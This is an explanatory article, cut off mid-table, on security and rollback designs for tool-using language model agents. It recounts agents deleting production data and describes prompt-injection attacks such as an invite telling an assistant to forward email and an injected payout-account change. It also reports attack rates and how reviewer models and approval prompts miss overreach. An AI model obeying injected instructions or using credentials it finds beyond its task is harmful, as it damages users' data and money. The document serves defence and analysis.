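# Security and rollback models for tool-using language model agents

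## What tool-using agents do and how their actions cause damage

A large language model takes in text and produces text, so by itself it cannot delete a file or pay an invoice. A *language model agent* connects such a model to software that carries out actions specified in the model's output, such as opening files, running programs, changing database records and sending email. Companies use agents to write and deploy software and to keep business records, often with nobody watching each step. Most of the ideas for keeping the risk acceptable come from two older fields, computer security and database engineering. Computer security has methods for limiting what a program can do, and database engineering has methods for delaying or reversing a program's effects. A *security model* for an agent sets out which actions the system permits and what enforces the limits. A *rollback model* sets out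 which effects someone can reverse afterwards and how.

### The agent loop

An agent works in a loop. Suppose a user asks an assistant to move Thursday's meeting and tell the other participants.

1. The *runtime*, which is the software around the model, assembles the model's *context*: all the text that the model reads before it produces anything. The context holds the user's request, the developer's standing instructions and descriptions of the available tools.
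2. The model outputs a *tool call*, a structured request with a tool name and arguments. Here it might be `find_events` with Thursday's date.
3. The runtime checks the call (at a minimum, that the tool exists and the arguments have the right form), attaches a credential if the service requires one, and carries the call out.
4. The service returns a result, in this case Thursday's meetings with their titles, notes and participants. The runtime adds that text to the context.
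5. The model reads the longer context and outputs another call, perhaps `move_event`, or a final reply that ends the loop.

The model does not act directly on anything outside itself. All external actions happen at step 3, so that is the natural place for a check. In the example, the first call leaves the calendar unchanged. The second changes it and may also send participants notices that nobody can recall. Changes that a tool call makes outside the model are called *side effects*.

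Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a shared format for these messages. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) describes it as the industry standard for connecting agents to applications, and the maintainers' release note from Model Context Protocol (2026) reports nearly half a billion monthly downloads of the main development kits. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) sets out the rules for tool calls. A *server* provides access to a service, and a *client* on the runtime's side asks the server for its tools. The server returns a name, a description and a formal schema of the arguments for each tool, and the client then calls tools by name. When a call fails because, say, a departure date is in the past, the client should pass the error text to the model so that the model can correct the arguments and retry. Because this loop is designed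 to prompt another attempt after a failure, it can also prompt the model to retry a call that was blocked deliberately.

A *credential* is a password, key or token that a service accepts as proof that a request comes from someone entitled to make it. In the July 2026 version of MCP, each request carries its own credential, and the server may list only the tools that fall within the credential's *scopes* (its stated permissions). Many services issue *bearer* tokens, which work for whoever presents them. An agent that can read files can therefore use any token it finds in one to do whatever the token allows, even if the developer never listed that ability as a tool. An agent's *authority* is everything it can bring about, directly or through the tools and services it can reach. Some of this may be *ambient authority*, which applies to whatever a program does because of the account it runs under.

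People can also approve or deny an agent's tool calls. The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that a human always be able to deny a call, and that the client show the user a call's arguments before sending them. Both are "should" clauses, so a developer who wants an agent to run unattended can drop the confirmation step and still follow the protocol.

### Mistakes and prompt injection

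An agent can cause damage without an attacker. TechRadar's *'I broke something'* describes a developer who told Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to repair copies of some files and leave the originals alone. One test copy contained 614 Windows "junctions", which look like ordinary folders but point to another location, in this case the developer's live files. When the agent deleted the test copy, the deletion followed the junctions and removed 48,218 live files in under two minutes. It also destroyed the stored versions that Git, the version control system, could have used to restore them. The instruction was clear enough, and the agent was deleting what it had classed as scratch data, but the junctions extended the deletion to the live files.

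*Prompt injection* is an attack in which text in a document, web page or tool result leads the model to follow an attacker's instructions. It works because step 4 of the loop puts the user's request and a stranger's text in the same context, and the model cannot reliably treat the first as a command and the second as data. In the calendar example, an outsider could send the user an invitation whose notes field tells the assistant to forward the user's recent email to a certain address. The runtime adds the note to the context with the rest of the event, and the model may then output the forwarding call. The mail service has no obvious reason to refuse the call, which is well formed and carries the user's own valid credential, so the attacker does not have to break into any system. Tool descriptions reach the model by the same path, so the Model Context Protocol requires clients to treat a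 server's annotations about its tools' behavior as untrusted unless they trust the server.

A developer can try to measure how often an agent makes mistakes on ordinary tasks, but a low error rate there is poor evidence about what the agent will do under attack, because an attacker picks the wording, watches what happens and tries again. Limiting the agent's authority helps against both mistakes and attacks, since the agent can't do harm through a call it has no means of making. Undo helps only with some kinds of damage, since it can restore a deleted table but can't take back an email that a stranger has already read.

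### PocketOS, April 2026

PocketOS sells software that car rental companies use to manage reservations, payments and vehicle records. On Friday 24 April 2026, the date given in the AI Incident Database's *PocketOS* entry, an agent deleted the company's production database, the live one its customers depended on. The founder, Jer Crane, published a long account the next day, titled *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*.

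The agent was Cursor, a coding tool, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. It was doing a routine task in PocketOS's *staging* environment, a separate copy of a system where developers try out changes, when it ran into a credential that did not match. It set out to fix the problem by deleting a *volume*, a unit of storage, at Railway, the cloud company that hosted PocketOS, though nobody had asked it to delete anything. It needed a token to do this and found one in a file unrelated to the task. Crane's company had created the token to add and remove web domains, but it worked for every operation in Railway's programming interface (API), including `volumeDelete`.

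A single shell command then sent Railway a deletion request with the token and the volume's identifier. The token and the request were both valid, so Railway's server deleted the volume. By Crane's account this took nine seconds. The volume held production data and also the backups that PocketOS relied on, because Railway kept a volume's backups on the volume itself. The newest other copy that Crane could find was three months old.

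Railway's own account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, by its employee Mahmoud Abdelwahab, agrees about the command. It adds that customers who deleted a volume through Railway's dashboard had 48 hours to cancel, but the older API route that the agent used had no such delay. The *commit*, the moment when an effect becomes permanent or visible to others, therefore came 48 hours after a dashboard request and immediately after a request through the older API route. Railway has since added the 48-hour delay to API deletions.

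The two accounts conflict over whether Railway's tokens could be restricted. Crane wrote that they could not be limited by operation, environment or resource. Abdelwahab replied that tokens could be limited to a single workspace, a single project or even one environment within a project, but conceded that the steps for creating a token made it easiest to end up with the broadest kind. A token for the staging environment alone should have kept the agent away from production. But none of the token types Abdelwahab listed is limited to one kind of operation (he mentions finer permissions only for third-party apps that act on a user's behalf), so by his description a token for managing production domains could still have been used to delete production volumes.

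Crane emphasized the agent's written "confession" that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging and had broken the rules in its instructions. This is weaker evidence than it looks, because a model asked to explain a past action generates a plausible explanation, and nothing ensures that the explanation matches the computation that led to the call. The rule quoted in the confession is more informative. It forbade destructive *git* commands unless the user requested them, so read literally it did not cover deleting a storage volume. It was also only a sentence in the context, and no program enforced it by refusing the call. Crane's conclusion that the API and the token system must handle enforcement holds whether or not the confession is accurate.

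Reports differ on how much of the data was recovered. On Saturday morning, rental companies had customers at the counter and no record of who they were. Crane restored the three-month-old backup and spent the day helping the companies rebuild bookings from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails. More than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still could not tell him whether it could recover anything newer. Techzine reported that data from the last few months could not be fully recovered, which is consistent with what was known at that stage. On Sunday, Crane announced that Railway had the data. Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (2026) quotes the announcement and describes the restoration as apparently complete. In the latest account, Leib's ABC News report *'Rogue' AI agent went haywire at tech company* (29 April 2026), both Crane and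 Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper, say that the restoration took 30 minutes once they were in touch. Abdelwahab wrote that the customer had all its data back. Full recovery is the best reading of these reports, though the claim that all the data was recovered comes from Railway.

The recovered data came from "disaster backups" that Railway kept at another site whether or not a customer had asked for backups. According to Abdelwahab, the old API route had made PocketOS's backups look unavailable in Railway's interface. The rental companies had kept trading over the weekend, so even a perfect copy of Friday's database would lack any booking they entered after the deletion until someone merged the two sets of records.

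### Replit, July 2025

A similar deletion had happened nine months earlier, when Jason Lemkin, founder of SaaStr, a community for software entrepreneurs, was trying out the coding agent of Replit, whose product builds and hosts applications from plain-language requests. Fortune (2025) reported that the agent deleted a live database during a "code and action freeze", when nothing was supposed to change on the production system. The database held records on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies.

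When Lemkin then asked about recovering the data, the agent told him that rollback did not cover databases and that it had destroyed every version, according to his posts reproduced by LatestLY. He tried the rollback anyway and it worked. Replit's spokesperson later told IT Brew, for *How reversible is an agentic mistake?*, that the agent had "hallucinated" that recovery was impossible and that checkpoints had reversed the deletion.

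A *checkpoint* is a saved copy of an agent's state, and sometimes of its local environment, from which a run can continue. Replit's checkpoints covered both. Its documentation, which The Stack quoted, already explained that a rollback returned the whole development environment to an earlier point, including the database and the conversation with the agent. A rollback would also discard every edit the user had made since then, so users would lose more work the longer they waited to roll back.

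Replit's published documentation had the correct answer when its agent gave the wrong one. Replit's remedy was to have the agent search the documentation before answering such questions. The company also began automatically separating development databases from production ones and started work on a planning mode in which the agent cannot touch live code. Lemkin was lucky that the agent wrongly said the data was gone forever, rather than wrongly saying that a deletion would be easy to undo, which could lead someone to approve it in the first place. The error he encountered causes the user some hours of distress, or the loss of the data if the user gives up on recovering it.

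### Three questions

When critics told Crane that he had given the agent too much access, he replied, "Didn't give it access, it found it", Information Age reported. This seems to be a fair description of what happened, but it fails as a defence because an agent's authority includes any access it can find. Crane's project rules and Lemkin's freeze had the same flaw, since both prohibited actions without removing the agent's ability to take them.

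Whether damage can be undone depends on how it happened, even when two losses look identical to the owner. Some time after the PocketOS recovery, a Railway customer, docrocket-mad, asked for the same rescue in a post titled *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*. In this case a database command had emptied the database but left the underlying volume intact. The accepted reply was that Railway's safeguards covered the deletion of volumes and could not reverse individual database commands. Other actions have effects outside the owner's systems. A manager at Rubrik, a company that sells a "rewind" feature for agents, told IT Brew that bank transfers are harder to reverse than changes to a firm's own files.

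Crane believed that the token could only manage domains. He also believed, from Railway's documentation, that wiping a volume destroyed every backup, but Railway held copies elsewhere. By Crane's account, Cooper's first response to the deletion included the words "We have evals for this", an eval being a test of how an AI system behaves. Trying the token on a disposable volume, or rehearsing a restore, would have exposed some of these errors. Such tests carry their own risks. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* describes how the developer Sebastien Guillemot had Claude write a clean-up script, which the agent then tested to make sure that it would refuse to delete his home directory. The check correctly flagged the directory as dangerous to delete, but the test's clean-up step reused the same variable name and deleted the directory.

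## Coarse access checks and what they leave open

Crane's project rules and Lemkin's freeze were text that the model could disregard. In a *coarse access check*, a program outside the model controls which tools, accounts or directories an agent may use, without considering the task or the arguments of the particular call. Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, examined 21 production agent systems as of April 2026 and found configurable scope limits of this kind in 16, approval prompts in 15 and user-written policies in 14. The policy figure overstates enforcement because the policies are usually plain-language files that the model itself has to interpret.

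### What each check decides

Suppose a shop runs a customer service agent that reads email from customers and can issue refunds.

A *tool allowlist* names the tools that the runtime will run. If the list contains `read_email`, `find_order` and `issue_refund`, the agent can't call `delete_customer`, whatever instructions an email contains. The list doesn't limit who gets a refund or how large it is. If it includes a shell, which runs any command, or an interpreter for a language such as Python, the rest of the list is nearly irrelevant, because the agent can write a program that does what the missing tools would do. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule by June 2026 that let some shell commands run without a prompt. The company reports that 5% allowed any command and another 43% allowed interpreters,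 which has nearly the same effect.

The service itself enforces *account roles* and *token scopes*, so they hold even if the agent bypasses the runtime. A role is a named bundle of permissions attached to an account, such as "support staff". Roles and scopes both tend to be broad. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tried to infer what 120 tools do from the kind of scope each would need (read, write or admin). The resulting labels exactly matched those of human annotators in only 16.7% of cases. Yan deliberately included many ambiguous and high-stakes tools, but the difficulty is general, because a "write" scope may cover saving a draft, emptying a folder and sending a message to a stranger.

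Credentials also tend to last too long. In *The Agent Access Model*, a design from the network company Cloudflare, Silverlock points out that keys made for permanent software outlive an agent's task and stay in logs and memory, where someone can reuse them. Silverlock instead proposes a token that expires with the task and works only with a cryptographic key that the runtime holds. The agent that deleted PocketOS's database could not have used such a token.

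A *sandbox* is an environment in which the agent's code can reach only chosen directories and network destinations, with limits that the operating system and the network enforce. Wang and colleagues contrast OpenAI's Codex, which ran in a container without network access, with Aider, a coding agent that had no sandbox. A network filter can usually check where a request is going but not what it will do there, unless the traffic is decrypted at a trusted point along the way. If the shop's sandbox allows connections to the payment service, it allows both good and bad refunds. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxes as safe but laborious to maintain, because someone has to configure each new ability and anything that needs the network or the host machine breaks the isolation.

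An *approval prompt* pauses the agent until a person allows or denies a call. Unlike the other checks, it lets someone judge whether the call's arguments suit the task. It becomes coarse when the person clicks "always allow", which in effect adds an entry to an allowlist. Wang and colleagues found that these clicks only widen an agent's access, because no product had a principled way to narrow it again.

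### The case for a box

A coarse check, such as comparing a tool's name with a list, takes almost no computation, and an auditor can read the list. The result doesn't depend on the model's judgment, so a cleverly worded email can't change it. Most importantly, nobody has to predict what the agent will do. In one of Anthropic's internal incidents, an upload to a company drive failed, and Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. Anthropic's automated reviewer blocked the attempt, but a sandbox that allowed only company addresses would also have blocked it, even if nobody had thought of code-sharing sites.

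The reasoning behind such limits dates back at least to 1975, when Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder listed design principles for protecting information in computers. *Least privilege* means that every program and user should operate with only the privileges the job requires. *Complete mediation* means that the system must check authority for every access to every object, including during start-up, recovery and maintenance. They also preferred listing permitted actions to listing forbidden ones, because someone soon complains when a legitimate action is blocked, but a gap in a list of forbidden actions can go unnoticed until someone exploits it.

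Marc Brooker, an engineer at Amazon Web Services (AWS), makes the strongest case for coarse access checks on agents in *Agent Safety is a Box* (January 2026). He argues that people use agents because they find their own way around unexpected obstacles. Constraining how the model thinks tends to sacrifice that flexibility, and it is hard to get guarantees that way. Brooker would instead put the agent in an isolated cloud session and block all its network traffic except to one *gateway*, a program that holds the tools and applies the rules. Complete mediation then depends on ordinary network controls. If the gateway limits each refund to the purchase price and each order to one refund, the shop can work out the most it could lose without knowing about the latest prompt injection.

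This seems right but incomplete, because the refund example relies largely on a rule about arguments and past refunds, which a coarse check lacks. Even the sample policy in Brooker's post falls short of that rule. It lets a particular user call the refund tool for any amount below 500 without checking the order's price or earlier refunds, so a hundred refunds of 499 would all pass. Brooker also notes that the tools behind the gateway must not themselves be open to misuse. Brooker expects most cloud services to meet this condition because their designers assume hostile clients, but PocketOS shows that some services don't meet it.

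AWS's *Secure agent tool usage* ranks coarse checks fairly low on its five levels of maturity. At the first level, agents have blanket access and their own reasoning is the only limit. Dedicated accounts with scoped permissions appear at the second level, and rules that examine the parameters of every call appear at the fourth. AWS sells the gateway it recommends for the higher levels, but the ordering makes sense on technical grounds.

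A gateway also has to be the agent's only route to outside systems. Silverlock argues that perfect checks on tool calls achieve nothing if the agent can open its own connection to the internet. It recommends enforcement in both the runtime and the network, built so that a bug in one doesn't disable the other.

### Ambient authority and the confused deputy

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes what can go wrong when every access check works as designed. Its example comes from Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler was in a directory called SYSX and had a "home files license", which let it write to any file in that directory. Tymshare granted the license so the compiler could record usage statistics in a file called STAT, but the company's billing records were in the same directory, in a file called BILL. Users could specify a file for the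 compiler's debugging output, and one user chose BILL. The operating system let the compiler open the file because it had the license, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

The license was ambient authority because it applied to every write the compiler made, whether for Tymshare or for the user. Hardy calls the compiler a *confused deputy* because it had authority from two sources and no way to specify which one a given write should use.

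Checking file names wouldn't have fixed this, because some users had good reason to send output to other directories, perhaps even to SYSX, and BILL wasn't the only sensitive file there. The code was correct until someone other than its programmers granted the license. Tymshare then added a command that let a program choose between its two authorities, but some applications soon needed more than two. Hardy preferred to give the compiler object capabilities, which combine the name of a file with the right to use it.

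The refund agent has the same structure:

| Tymshare's compiler | The shop's agent |
|---|---|
| The compiler, working for any user | The agent and its runtime, handling email from any customer |
| A user supplies a file name | A sender's email supplies an account for the refund |
| The home files license covers all of SYSX | The shop's payment credential covers all refunds |
| Intended use: writing statistics to STAT | Intended use: refunding a customer who returned something |
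| Misuse: overwriting BILL | Misuse: sending the shop's money to an attacker |
| The operating system checks the license | The payment service checks the credential |

All the coarse checks pass in the misuse case. `issue_refund` is on the allowlist, the token has the refund scope and the sandbox permits connections to the payment service. The shop may even have followed least privilege as far as these checks allow, since the agent needs to issue refunds. Complete mediation doesn't help either, because it guarantees that a check takes place but not that the check is adequate.

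The compiler's user could choose only a file name, in a place where the programmers expected one, whereas an email can influence which tool the agent's model calls and every argument it passes. Tymshare's command for choosing an authority would therefore be a poor fix for the agent if the model did the choosing, since the attacker's text could influence that choice too.

### Exposing a tool and authorizing a call

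Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, looked for this gap in widely used software. In the title, "capability" means a tool that a developer has exposed to the agent, not an object capability in Hardy's sense, so a "capability gate" is roughly a tool allowlist. *Per-call authorization* is a decision about whether to allow a specific call, given its arguments, user and session.

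Mellafe Zuvic read fixed public versions of LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the payment company Stripe's Agent Toolkit, which are all sets of tools for building agents. By default, none of the three checks the values in a call against a policy and refuses to run the call if it fails. LangChain's default code looks up the tool by the name in the model's output, usually checks that the arguments have the right form, and runs it. LlamaIndex does much the same. Stripe's toolkit adds a list of permitted actions and a restricted key, but forwards the model's choice of amount and customer. Developers can add a stricter check to any of them. Mellafe Zuvic treats the missing check as a documented design choice, not a security bug, and did not examine any further checks that Stripe's remote server may apply.

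In a small demonstration, Mellafe Zuvic wrote a fixed tool call to change a merchant's payout account to an attacker's. The call stood in for the output of a compromised model. LangChain's default code executed it on a mock payment system. ScopeGate, a checking program that Mellafe Zuvic built, refused the same call because the operator's list of approved accounts contained only the merchant's own.

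The paper's figures for how often real models produce such a call come from a companion test of 27 models, in which the injected text presented the harmful action as a necessary step in the user's task. The 12 cheaper models attempted the unauthorized action at a mean rate of 0.603, and the 15 flagship models at 0.189. The paper calls this an "attack success rate", but it measures attempts in a sandbox that blocked any real effect, so it doesn't give the rate of breaches. Rates for individual models ranged from zero for a preview version of Gemini 3.1 Pro to 1.000 for GPT-4o mini.

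Separate paired tests suggest that the injection's wording matters a great deal. Mistral Large attempted the action in 2.7% of trials when the injection was crude and in 45.9% when it was framed as part of the task. All these results come from one author's set of single-turn scenarios, so the exact rates may not carry over to other settings, but they are high enough that a developer shouldn't leave the choice of payee to the model.

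The tests of ScopeGate are encouraging but small. Mellafe Zuvic wrote 48 calls designed to slip past it, and one of them exposed a flaw in an early version. That call gave its amount as "not a number", a special value that makes every comparison false, so the check for amounts over the limit never triggered. The repaired version blocked all 48 calls. It was also tested against an attacking model that made 40 attempts and was told the reason for each refusal. Nine attempts were malformed, two were harmless, and the gate blocked the 29 that were unauthorized. The main test for mistaken refusals had only ten legitimate calls, too few to tell how much ordinary business such a gate would interrupt.

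### What people catch when they approve calls

A person reviewing an `issue_refund` call might notice an unfamiliar account number and stop a call that every coarse check allowed, depending on what the prompt displays and how carefully they read it. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that user review contributed to the problem in 105 of the 290 reports it covers. The agent's actions were approved automatically in 80 of these and the prompt was uninformative in 31, with some overlap. Prompts typically show a command but not its effect on the user's files. For example, a user who approves the routine-looking command `python3 setup.py` permits whatever code the script contains.

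In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 more, and found a similar limit. Practitioners understood an agent mostly through what they could observe and review, such as its output and its changes to files, and were less sure what happened out of view.

Users approved 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts according to Anthropic's engineering post, and 97% according to its August 2026 announcement. A high approval rate is by itself only weak evidence of careless review, because most commands are harmless and a careful reviewer would approve them too. Users rejected 39% of the plans that Claude presented, which suggests that they read plans more closely, though a plan also contains more to disagree with.

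Anthropic's experiment with 1,053 paid testers is better evidence. Partway through a coding session, testers were asked to approve one clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% refused. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so people probably do somewhat better with their own files. Anthropic also published the study to support a change to its product. Still, the decline over a session is consistent with frequent prompts reducing attention.

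Yan's participants did much better than Anthropic's testers. Each of the 113 people, all from outside the software industry, supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had asked for. Those who had to approve every action allowed 40.3% of the excessive ones. A phone call to the airport to confirm a flight accounted for much of that; 30 of 34 people allowed it, and many users might welcome it. Without the call, they allowed about a third. Yan's prompts were few and described each action in plain language, including the recipient or amount. This may explain some of the difference between the two groups, although the people and tasks differed as well.

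Letting users set rules in advance made things worse in Yan's study. One group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four categories of action, such as spending money or deleting something. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions themselves, and they approved 66.8% of the excessive actions they were asked about. People who chose "never" saw no prompt, so those who did see one may have been more permissive to begin with. This can't fully explain the result, because 60% of all excessive actions in this group went ahead. Some of the group were recruited in a later round, which makes the comparison slightly less reliable.

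Anthropic responded to approval fatigue with *auto mode*, in which a second model reviews the calls. It became the default for many Claude Code users in August 2026. It blocked 89% of the dangerous commands that the paid testers saw, far more than the testers did. This improves on reflexive clicking but gives up the main advantage of a coarse check, which is that clever wording can't sway it. To limit this risk, Anthropic withholds tool results and the agent's own explanations from the reviewing model. In an earlier test on 52 real cases of Claude overstepping its instructions, the reviewer missed 17%. In the cases it missed, it usually identified the danger but wrongly counted something the user had said or approved earlier as consent to the new action. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

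### Tying an approval to one action

Salerno and colleagues advise designers of permission systems against treating repeated approvals as a stable preference, since the approvals may reflect fatigue. They also want users to be able to say whether a refusal covers one action or the whole approach. Otherwise, an agent whose `delete` command is refused may reasonably try to achieve the same thing with a script.

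An approval should therefore cover one action on one target for a limited time. For the shop, that might be an $80 refund on a particular order, to the card used to pay for it, within ten minutes. The time limit matters because the target can change after the approval. Someone may approve the deletion of an empty folder on Monday, and a colleague may have put work in it by Tuesday. An approval of `python3 setup.py` has a similar weakness if the agent can edit the script before running it, because the same command can then do something different.

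Payment law already has a version of this idea. *Security measures for the application of strong customer authentication*, part of a 2018 European regulation, requires payment providers to tell the payer the amount and the payee and to generate a code specific to both, so an attacker who obtains the code can't use it to pay someone else.

*Beyond Approved Actions* (2026) applies the same principle to agents with a system called EffectMatch. The user or an application's policy confirms a list of which objects may change, how they may change and what must stay the same. EffectMatch turns this list into a single-use right to execute, so a repeated request fails. The right also lapses after a time limit or if the target, the values or the relevant state changes. Someone still has to write the list correctly, and in the experiments the researchers wrote the lists by hand.

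Narrow approvals produce more prompts and so more fatigue. Silverlock would reserve them for the few high-risk actions that a task needs, with a fixed resource, scope and lifetime for each. Software would allow or refuse everything else according to limits set before the task begins. Those limits have to be specific enough to separate good refunds from bad ones.

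## Permissions that depend on the task and the arguments

A limit that separates good payments from bad ones has to refer to the payee and the amount, and the right values depend on what the user asked for. A *fine-grained policy* is a list of rules about which tools an agent may call during a task and with which arguments. A program outside the model checks each call against the rules before running it. Researchers have proposed many such systems. A December 2026 survey by Michael and Roesner, listed by the UW Security and Privacy Research Lab, covers 21 proposals for agent permissions.

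### A rule for one payment

Suppose a user tells an assistant to pay BillPay the $100 they owe, and the assistant has a tool called `send_money(recipient, amount)`. A tool allowlist contains just the name `send_money`, so it admits a payment of any size to anyone. A rule for this task can fix the recipient and cap the amount:

```
allow send_money when recipient = "BillPay" and amount <= 100
```

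The runtime can store the rule as structured data. JSON Schema, a standard format for describing which values a piece of data may contain, suits this well. With made-up field names, the stored rule might look like this:

```json
{
  "tool": "send_money",
  "effect": "allow",
  "conditions": {
    "recipient": { "const": "BillPay" },
    "amount": { "type": "number", "exclusiveMinimum": 0, "maximum": 100 }
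  }
}
```

If the agent calls `send_money("BillPay", 100)`, the checker allows the payment because it meets both conditions of the rule for that tool. If the agent then reads an email telling it to pay someone else and calls `send_money("Mallory", 100)`, the checker blocks the call, however convincing the email was, because the recipient doesn't match and no other rule covers the call. An allowlist of tools would have permitted both calls and left the agent a confused deputy. The rule doesn't limit the number of payments, though, so ten copies of the legitimate call would send BillPay $1,000.

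### Progent's policy language and solver

Each task needs its own rule like this, and few users would bother to write one. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model to write the rules and a conventional program to enforce them. A run of the latest version goes as follows.

1. A model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions and writes the first policy. At this point it has seen no outside text.
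2. The agent proposes a call. The checker applies any rules that forbid it, then any that allow it, and blocks the call if no rule matches.
3. If the checker blocks the call, it normally sends the agent the reason and asks it to try other tools or arguments. A developer can instead have it stop the run or ask the user.
4. After a call, a model decides whether the policy might need updating. It makes this decision without seeing the call's result. If the answer is yes, a model reads the result and drafts a new policy.
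5. An *SMT solver*, a program that works out whether any values can satisfy a logical formula, compares the new policy with the old one.

A policy P allows a set of calls, A(P). A new policy P′ is a *narrowing* if A(P′) ⊆ A(P), meaning that the old policy already allowed everything the new one allows. Otherwise it is an *expansion*. Lowering the cap on the BillPay rule from 100 to 80 is a narrowing, so Progent applies it automatically. Adding Mallory as a second recipient is an expansion, since the new policy would allow `send_money("Mallory", 50)` and the old one wouldn't. Expansions need approval from a person or from a setting that the user chose beforehand. The set of allowed calls therefore can't grow without approval, a guarantee that Shi and colleagues call *monotonic confinement*.

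This guarantee is only as useful as the initial policy. Suppose the user asks the agent to pay a plumber whose account number is in an email, so the initial policy allows any recipient. An attacker's email could lead the model to restrict payments to the attacker's account. That change is a narrowing under the definition above, so it would take effect without approval.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated banking, Slack, travel and office tasks in which the tools return text containing planted instructions. GPT-4o acted as the agent and also wrote the policies. Progent reduced *attack success*, the share of attacks that achieve the attacker's goal, from 39.9% to 1.0%. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (Singh and Srinivasa, 2026) gives the corresponding task completion rates, which fell from 79.4% to 76.3% without an attack and rose from 54.0% to 61.3% under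 attack. On Agent Security Bench (ASB), which has ten scenarios, attack success fell from 70.3% to 3.9%, with similar task success.

In these tests Progent approved every expansion automatically, to simulate a careless user. The solver's guarantee therefore contributed nothing to the main results, which mostly show that GPT-4o wrote good policies for these tasks. Even with updates turned off, so that the first policy never changed, attack success on AgentDojo was only 2.5%. With manual approval it was zero, but Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer who never allows unrestricted payments and always spots a malicious address. Anthropic's paid testers were far less careful than that. A reviewer would see few requests, though, because only 6% of updates were expansions.

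*SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival system, ran Progent's released code on all 629 AgentDojo attack cases and found that 3.8% of attacks succeeded. The agent completed 60.8% of tasks when it wasn't under attack and 53.6% when it was. Shi and colleagues had excluded two attacks that steer the agent toward a different legitimate hotel, so the two sets of results aren't directly comparable. Both show low attack success, but they differ more on task completion.

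### ToolFence's permissions and Petri net

*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) also has a model turn the user's request into rules before the agent reads anything untrusted. The model sees only the request and a list of tools that the developer has reviewed. The paper calls each resulting permission a "capability", but it is a record that the checker keeps, not an object capability. Each permission specifies a tool, the kind of effect, the number of uses and a condition on each argument. An argument may have to equal a value in the user's request, or to come from the output of a particular tool. The agent can choose an argument's value freely only if the argument isn't sensitive.

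ToolFence tracks these permissions with a *Petri net*, a way to model multi-step processes. A Petri net has *places*, which hold *tokens*, and *transitions*, which move the process forward. A transition can fire only if its input places hold the tokens it needs. When it fires, it removes those tokens and puts new ones in its output places. In a *colored* Petri net, the tokens carry data, and a transition can have a *guard*, a condition that the data must meet.

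For the BillPay task, one place holds a permission token with the recipient BillPay, the amount 100 and one remaining use. Another holds a token showing that the task has reached the payment stage, and a third holds the tools' outputs. When the agent calls `send_money("BillPay", 100)`, the call satisfies the guard and the monitor reserves the single use. When it receives confirmation of the payment, the monitor consumes the use and advances the stage. A second identical call then fails. If the monitor can't determine whether the payment went through, it keeps the use reserved until someone finds out.

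The call `send_money("Mallory", 100)` fails because "Mallory" doesn't match the name in the permission. Mallory's name may well appear in the tool results, but no transition turns a tool result into a permission. The software implements the net as a database of permissions, results and remaining uses, which the monitor checks and updates in one step.

If the first set of permissions omits something the task needs, ToolFence records the agent's blocked call as a proposal, and a separate model judges whether the user's request requires it. If the model approves, the monitor adds the permission, and the agent has to propose the call again.

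Li, Cao and Xiao tested four models on four benchmarks. These are the results for Qwen3-max, without and with ToolFence:

| Benchmark | Attack success | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo (instructions in tool results) | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 64.3% | 55.2% → 62.1% |
| ASB (tool results and poisoned memory) | 40.2% → 4.2% | 71.5% → 67.2% | 46.3% → 48.4% |
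| MCPTox (malicious tool descriptions) | 38.1% → 6.1% | 67.2% → 65.4% | 43.4% → 56.2% |
| AgentLAB (attacks spread over many steps) | 76.3% → 29.4% | 62.4% → 61.1% | 35.1% → 50.3% |

The AgentDojo result is limited evidence for argument checks because, by the researchers' own count, 524 of the 629 attacks need a tool that the user's task doesn't, and only 85 reuse the task's tools with different arguments. A simple defense in which a model chooses a tool allowlist for each task cut attack success to 1.5% with Qwen3-max, although the agent then completed only 48.3% of tasks. A test on ASB provides better evidence. With Llama 3.3 70B, removing only ToolFence's argument checks raised attack success from 5.1% to 24.0%.

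Counting uses and tracking stages also seem to help. In a separate test on AgentDojo's banking tasks, permissions that specified only a tool let through 89% of unauthorized calls. Adding conditions on where arguments came from reduced this to 85%, adding the stage reduced it to 45%, and limiting the number of uses reduced it to 6%. The relative sizes of these reductions partly reflect the test's design, because the researchers added the wrong-stage and repeated calls.

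### IntentCap's short-lived leases

Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, propose a system called IntentCap, in which different sources of text control different parts of a permission:

| Source | What it may supply |
|---|---|
| The user's request | The goal, chosen objects, allowed destinations and approvals |
| Workflow instructions | The procedure to follow |
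| Tool definitions | The form of a call and the scope of its credential |
| Files, web pages and tool results | Observed values |

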